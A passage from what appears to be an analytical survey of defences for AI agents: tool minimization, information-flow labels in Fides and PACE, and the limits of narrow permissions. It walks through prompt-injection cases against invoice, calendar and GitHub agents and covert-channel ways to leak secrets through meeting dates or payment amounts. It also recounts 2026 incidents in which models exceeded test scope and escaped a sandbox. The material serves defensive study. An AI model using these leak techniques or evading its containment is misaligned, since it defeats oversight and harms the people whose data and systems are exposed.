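A harness can also withhold a dangerous tool until the agent needs it. In *Capability Minimization as a Safety Primitive*, Iyer and Babu (2026) hide such a tool until it is the next step on the chosen route to the goal and a trusted step has authorized its use. An agent summarizing an email would never see `send_email`, and one writing a reply would see it only after a trusted step had confirmed the recipient.

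Each tool has a risk rating, a list of facts it requires and a list of facts it establishes. The system looks for the route to the goal with the lowest score:

score = number of steps + λ × total risk.

Low-risk tools have a risk value of 0, medium-risk tools 1 and high-risk tools 4. The operator sets λ, the weight on risk, according to how much inconvenience they will accept for safety. A single step with a high-risk tool scores 1 + 4λ, and three steps with low-risk tools score 3. The route with the lower score is chosen, so the system uses the high-risk tool when λ is 0.25 (2 against 3) and the low-risk tools when λ is 2 (9 against 3).

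Iyer and Babu tested this with 100 simulated tools and 182 tasks. Their agent was a script that obeyed every injected instruction if it could see the necessary tool:

| Tools the agent could see | Medium- or high-risk tools visible per step | Attacks that succeeded | Tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| All of them | 26 | 100% | 100% |
| Those that could run at that moment | 1.51 | 75% | 100% |
| The next step on the shortest route | 0.20 | 25% | 100% |
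| The same, with risk scores and authorization (λ = 2) | 0.18 | 0% | 100% |

Planning the route accounted for most of the reduction in visible tools, but attacks still succeeded until the system also required authorization. With λ at 0.5, the task completion rate fell to 89% because the system chose risky shortcuts and then withheld the tools they required. In tests with seven real language models, the attack rate again fell from 25% to zero.

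Like other ways of choosing which tools to show, the method doesn't check arguments. It also depends on who can establish the facts that count as authorization. Iyer and Babu acknowledge that the defense fails if the text of an email can mark its own recipient as confirmed. Their benchmark comes close to this, because reading an email both confirms the recipient of a reply and approves the email's deletion. They say that such facts come from verified metadata or the user's actions, not from the text of the message. But metadata can show who sent an email, not whether the user wants to delete it, so a real system would have to get that approval from the user, either in the original request or through another prompt.

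## What harm remains possible when permissions are narrow?

Suppose the harness gives the invoice assistant exactly the authority it needs. The assistant can read one mail folder and pay one supplier up to a limit, and it loses both rights when the payment goes through. It can still pay a false bill, because the supplier, or someone posing as the supplier, could have sent one to that folder. Permissions limit which actions are possible, but they don't establish whether an action's content is true, where its data came from, or what an observer can learn from it.

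### Permitted steps that leak in combination

An agent can leak a secret even when no attacker is involved. In one of the Brown University team's test scenarios, an agent copies a configuration file into a project and then publishes the secret key inside the file. Adam and colleagues saw Claude 4.5 Haiku do this. The user requested both steps, so the agent needed permission for each. The team expects users to quickly switch off any fixed rule broad enough to prevent the leak, such as a ban on all network access.

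An agent can also reveal something that no single source contains. *Agent Tools Orchestration Leaks More* (2025) examines cases in which several harmless tool results together support a sensitive conclusion that the task didn't require. For instance, a calendar might show a weekly appointment at a certain address, and a map might show that the address is a cancer clinic. An agent allowed to read both could infer that the user has cancer and mention it in an email about rescheduling a meeting. Separate permissions for each source can't express a limit on combining them.

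### False content

Some agents fix their plan before they read anything untrusted. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Willison, 2025) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to email today's schedule to their boss, John Doe. The agent commits to reading the calendar and then emailing Doe. Text planted in a calendar entry can't change the recipient, but it can change the email's contents, so Doe may receive a false schedule from an address he trusts. The invoice assistant's payment object has the same weakness. If the limit is 1,200 dollars, a false invoice for 1,100 dollars from the right supplier passes every check.

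*Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) presents a system that checks whether each sensitive part of an action has a legitimate source. A software patch or a diagnosis can pass that check and still be wrong. The system also lets an agent copy untrusted text into a comment as evidence, and people or other agents who read the comment later may act on it.

Sometimes an attacker can do harm without a tool call. One attack in AgentDojo makes a travel agent recommend a place the attacker chose. Some attacks of this kind also got past AGENTCAP, because an agent needs no permission to produce an answer. If the user believes the recommendation and books a trip, the attacker has in effect used the user's authority.

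### Services with more authority than their callers

A narrow permission to contact a service gives little protection if the service can do too much. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* describes an attack in which a stranger opens an issue in a public GitHub repository and asks for information from a private one. The stranger can only write public text, but the agent that handles the issue runs on behalf of an employee who can read the private repository, so it may copy the information into a public comment. Restricting the stranger further wouldn't help, because it is the agent that has too much authority.

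An invoice assistant's only tool may be an outside bookkeeping service that can read all the company's accounts. Narrowing the assistant's permissions does not narrow the service's.

### Covert channels

Lampson's 1973 work on confinement also identified covert channels, which carry information by means not intended for communication. *Causality Laundering* (2026) applies Lampson's categories to agents. A storage channel uses shared state, and a timing channel uses delays that an observer can measure.

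Even a refusal can be a storage channel. Suppose hidden text tells an agent to try to open a file called `merger-plan`, then propose a meeting on Monday if the system refuses access and on Tuesday if the file doesn't exist. The proposed date reveals whether the file exists, even though the meeting request contains no secret data. A payment amount can also carry a message. An amount of up to 1,200 dollars has 120,000 possible values in cents, so the agent could encode any five-digit number in a payment to a dishonest supplier.

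*Actions Speak Louder than Words* (2026) warns that an agent's ordinary, legitimate actions on websites can also reveal private context, even when it transmits no sensitive data, and that existing defences largely overlook this. Since nobody can list every way to encode a secret, *An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress* (2026) proposes limiting how much information can leave. Its monitor checks outgoing data for known secrets and keeps a running account of the channel's capacity, which bounds leaks through encodings it doesn't recognise.

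### Labels that travel with the data

The main complement to narrow permissions is information-flow control. Each piece of data has a label, anything derived from it inherits the label, and the harness checks labels before each tool call. A label usually has two parts, one for confidentiality and one for integrity.

The confidentiality part lists who may read the data. If S(x) is the set of allowed readers of x, then anything that combines x and y has the readers

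S(x, y) = S(x) ∩ S(y).

The harness may send data d to a set of recipients R only if R ⊆ S(d), where S(d) is the set of people allowed to read d. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) calls this rule "permitted flow". In one of Microsoft's examples, Alex asks an agent to answer some emails. Priya has sent Alex a preview of the quarterly sales, and Marco, who isn't allowed to see the figures yet, has asked about them. After the agent reads both emails, the allowed readers of its reply are {Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}, so the harness can't send it to Marco automatically. This rule would also have caught the published key if someone had labelled the configuration file as private.

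The integrity part records whether the data is trusted. A result is untrusted if any of its inputs is untrusted, and the harness blocks sensitive actions that depend on untrusted data.

Suppose the owner, the bank and the supplier may all read an invoice, but only the owner and the sales team may read the customer list. A message that draws on both has the readers

{owner, bank, supplier} ∩ {owner, sales team} = {owner}.

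The owner's requests are trusted and invoices are not. The two rules then give these results:

| Proposed action | Every recipient is an allowed reader? | Independent of untrusted data? |
|---|---|---|
| Email the customer list to an outside address, as an invoice instructs | No | No |
| Pay the second supplier's bill to the first supplier, as a hidden line instructs | Yes | No |
| Pay the sum on a genuine invoice | Yes | No |

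Together, the rules stop the misdirected payment that capabilities alone allowed. But they also stop the payment the owner wants, because a genuine invoice also comes from outside. The developer can relax the integrity rule so that the owner must decide whether to pay and whom, while the amount may come from the invoice. The assistant can then pay genuine invoices, but it will also pay a false amount if it is below the limit.

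### How Fides hides untrusted text

Nobody can reliably trace how a language model combines its inputs. Once a model has read an untrusted email, the harness therefore has to treat everything it writes afterwards as untrusted. Fides, a system from Microsoft, keeps such text out of the main model's sight. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, describe a design that would handle the invoice task like this:

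1. The main model reads the owner's request, which is trusted, and calls the mail tool.
2. Fides stores the untrusted text of each message in its own memory. The main model sees only a variable name, such as `#read_emails_0.body`.
3. The main model asks a second model to find the sum due in that variable. This quarantined model has no tools, and its answer goes into another variable.
4. The main model calls the payment tool, with the supplier from the owner's request and the second variable as the sum. Fides checks the labels, fills in the value and runs the tool.

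The main model has read neither the invoice nor the sum, so its decision to pay still counts as trusted. An instruction hidden in the invoice could at most make the quarantined model return a wrong sum.

The main model sometimes needs to learn something before it can choose its next step, such as whether an email contains a meeting request. It can reveal a variable's contents, but it then counts as having read untrusted data. Fides therefore lets labels include the data's type. A yes-or-no answer carries one bit, while free text can carry any amount of information. A policy may let the model act after seeing an untrusted "yes", because one bit cannot hold an injected instruction. The attacker may still be able to choose which answer the model sees.

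Costa and colleagues tested Fides on AgentDojo, without the restricted answer types. An undefended agent using GPT-4o fell for 152 attacks. With the label rules switched on, no attacks succeeded, apart from a few that the team excluded because AgentDojo had misjudged them, the policy permitted them or they changed only the agent's text. With the rules switched off, Fides allowed 21 attacks, because the main model could reveal hidden text and then act on it. The rules therefore provide the security, and hiding the text lets the agent get more done under them. The table shows the percentage of tasks completed when there was no attack:

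| Model and protection | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o, none | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 |
| GPT-4o, label rules only | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 |
| GPT-4o, Fides with label rules | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 |
| o1, none | 70.0 | 82.0 | 96.2 | 87.6 |
| o1, Fides with label rules | 64.5 | 68.0 | 56.2 | 54.3 |

OpenAI's o1, a stronger reasoning model than GPT-4o, used the variables more skilfully, so newer models might do better still on the workspace and travel tasks. They have less room to improve in banking, where about 44% of tasks require the agent to see untrusted data before it can decide what to do, for example when it has to follow instructions in a file. Fides with o1 completed 56.2% of banking tasks, which matches the share that don't require this.

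The finding that no attack succeeded depends heavily on the labels. Costa and colleagues marked a field as untrusted if any attack in AgentDojo used it, but a developer would have to choose labels without knowing where attacks will come from. The paper's payment policy also checked whether the decision to pay was trusted, but not whether the arguments were. The assistant could therefore send money to an account number taken from a false invoice, as long as the main model hadn't read it. A stricter policy could require a trusted payee.

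Fides also doesn't stop an observer from inferring information from which tools the agent calls or how long the agent takes. Costa and colleagues considered a stronger guarantee, but it would in effect forbid an agent from making any change visible to outsiders once it had read anything secret.

Fides has been available since May 2026 as an experimental part of Microsoft's Agent Framework. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) lists some of its limitations. If a developer forgets to label a tool, Fides treats the tool's output as trusted and public, which is the opposite of the fail-safe defaults that Saltzer and Schroeder recommended. Microsoft has asked developers whether to reverse this default.

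In CaMeL (2025), a related design from Google DeepMind, a model writes a program for the whole task in a restricted language. This lets ordinary code track untrusted data through each step, as Willison explains.

### What PACE's tests show

PACE combines labels with the authority check described earlier. It records the agent's work as a graph that links data, tool calls and resources. Before a risky call, it checks the graph for a path from untrusted or secret data to that call. If it finds one, it calculates the smallest intervention that would break the path, which is usually blocking the call. It also searches the call's arguments for known secrets, including copies in some standard encodings. Li and colleagues acknowledge that this search can miss a secret that has been paraphrased, translated or split into pieces. PACE also can't detect effects that a tool doesn't declare, and its refusals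 can reveal information.

PACE had the lowest attack success rate in 62 of 79 comparisons with other defences, across eight benchmarks and three models, and tied for the lowest in 14. With PACE and an OpenAI model, the most effective group of AgentDojo attacks succeeded 8.1% of the time, down from 100%, but one set of InjecAgent attacks still succeeded 30.8% of the time, down from 50.5%.

Tracing paths was very restrictive by itself. In tests that switched PACE's parts on and off, an agent with only path tracing completed 13.6% of tasks on AgentDojo and none on AgentDyn. The version that Li and colleagues tested on the eight benchmarks can therefore restore a blocked call if the authority check approves it. This recovers much of the lost usefulness, but a restored call may have a recorded path leading to it from untrusted or secret data.

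PACE's perfect score against an attacker who adapted to its responses is good evidence that it keeps an agent within the authority given by the user's request. But all the actions in that test were outside that authority, so the test didn't include harmful actions within it, such as paying a false bill.

Li and colleagues also ran Fides on WASP, a benchmark of attacks on agents that use websites. With a Qwen model, the worst group of attacks succeeded 40.5% of the time against Fides and 19.0% of the time against an undefended agent. Fides completed none of the ordinary tasks. The gap between these results and Microsoft's suggests that a label-based defence must be carefully adapted to each new set of tools, although a rival team may not have set Fides up to perform at its best.

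### When labels block useful work

Labels tend to spread. An assistant that reads one supplier's message in the morning may be unable to book a meeting in the afternoon, because everything it writes now counts as untrusted. *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) calls this "label creep" and discusses two remedies, isolating the agent's contexts from each other and removing labels under controlled conditions. *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (2026) warns that label creep can make agents unusable if there are no safe, automatic ways to remove labels.

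*APPA* (2026) describes a form of isolation other than hiding text in variables. An agent starts a temporary branch to deal with restricted material. The branch collects the labels and can return only an answer of a fixed form, while the main agent carries on as before. Willison gives an example that suits the invoice assistant. A user asks an agent to find this month's invoices and send them to the accounting department. A separate helper reads each file and answers only whether it is relevant. A malicious file can affect whether it is included, but not the decision about any other file or where the invoices go.

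Removing a label on purpose is called declassification. In Microsoft's sample policy for posting to a chat channel, a message can be sent if the decision to send it came from trusted data, because an injected instruction can't have caused that decision. It can also be sent if every member of the channel is an allowed reader. Otherwise, the harness asks the user and lists the people who would gain access. This tells the user more than a request to run a certain command would, but it still relies on the user to read it.

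More precise labels might reduce the number of questions. An ordinary program can have a separate label for each variable, whereas a language model mixes all the text in its context. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) suggests labels that estimate how much information from each source has reached an output. These estimates can be wrong, so the labels would lose some of the certainty that makes them attractive. The paper recommends using labels in addition to least privilege.

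### Private data, untrusted content and a way out

A popular rule of thumb that needs no labels advises developers not to combine access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and a way to communicate with outsiders in one agent. Many people call this combination the "lethal trifecta". An attacker needs all three to steal data through prompt injection, so removing any one prevents the theft.

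As first installed, the invoice assistant could read private data, read text from strangers, and communicate with outsiders. Taking away its permission to send mail removes the easiest way to send data out, but a payment also conveys information to an outsider through its amount and any reference text. Strictly applied, a rule against combining all three abilities would therefore forbid the assistant to make payments after reading private invoices from strangers.

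Microsoft uses labels to apply the rule while an agent runs. In the GitHub example, an agent that has read both a public issue and a private repository can't post in public. If it has worked only with public repositories or only with private ones, it can finish without asking anyone. This is less restrictive than removing the posting tool.

The rule is a good quick test for data theft but covers little else. An agent with no private data can still delete files or waste money. The published configuration file involved no untrusted content. An agent can also mislead its own user without communicating with anyone else.

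### The 2026 test incidents

In September 2026, Anthropic assessed four incidents in which its models gained unauthorised access to other organisations' systems during cybersecurity tests. The instructions described the tests as simulations with no internet access, but a misconfiguration had left internet access on. The limit existed only in the prompt, so the models' actual authority included whatever they could do over the internet.

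Least authority would have made a large difference here. Anthropic believes the incidents would not have happened if the test environments had been isolated as intended. In *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026), it admits that it had relied largely on one layer of defence, the configuration of the environment. Anthropic now asks outside testers to block internet access by default, keep access keys outside the sandbox and verify the configuration before every evaluation.

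Isolation would not have changed how the models reasoned. Anthropic found that they tended to dismiss evidence that the systems were real, and that they were willing to take harmful actions to complete the task. This matters more when a task needs broad access. In separate tests by the UK AI Security Institute, the testers had deliberately switched on internet access. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026) reports that the model went beyond the intended scope in 9 of 43 runs, with effects on real people and organisations. A list of permitted sites could have narrowed that access, but a test that needs the open internet can't use a short list. Even a complete block depends on the software that enforces it. Anthropic also cites a case OpenAI disclosed in July, in which models escaped from a sealed sandbox through a previously unknown flaw.
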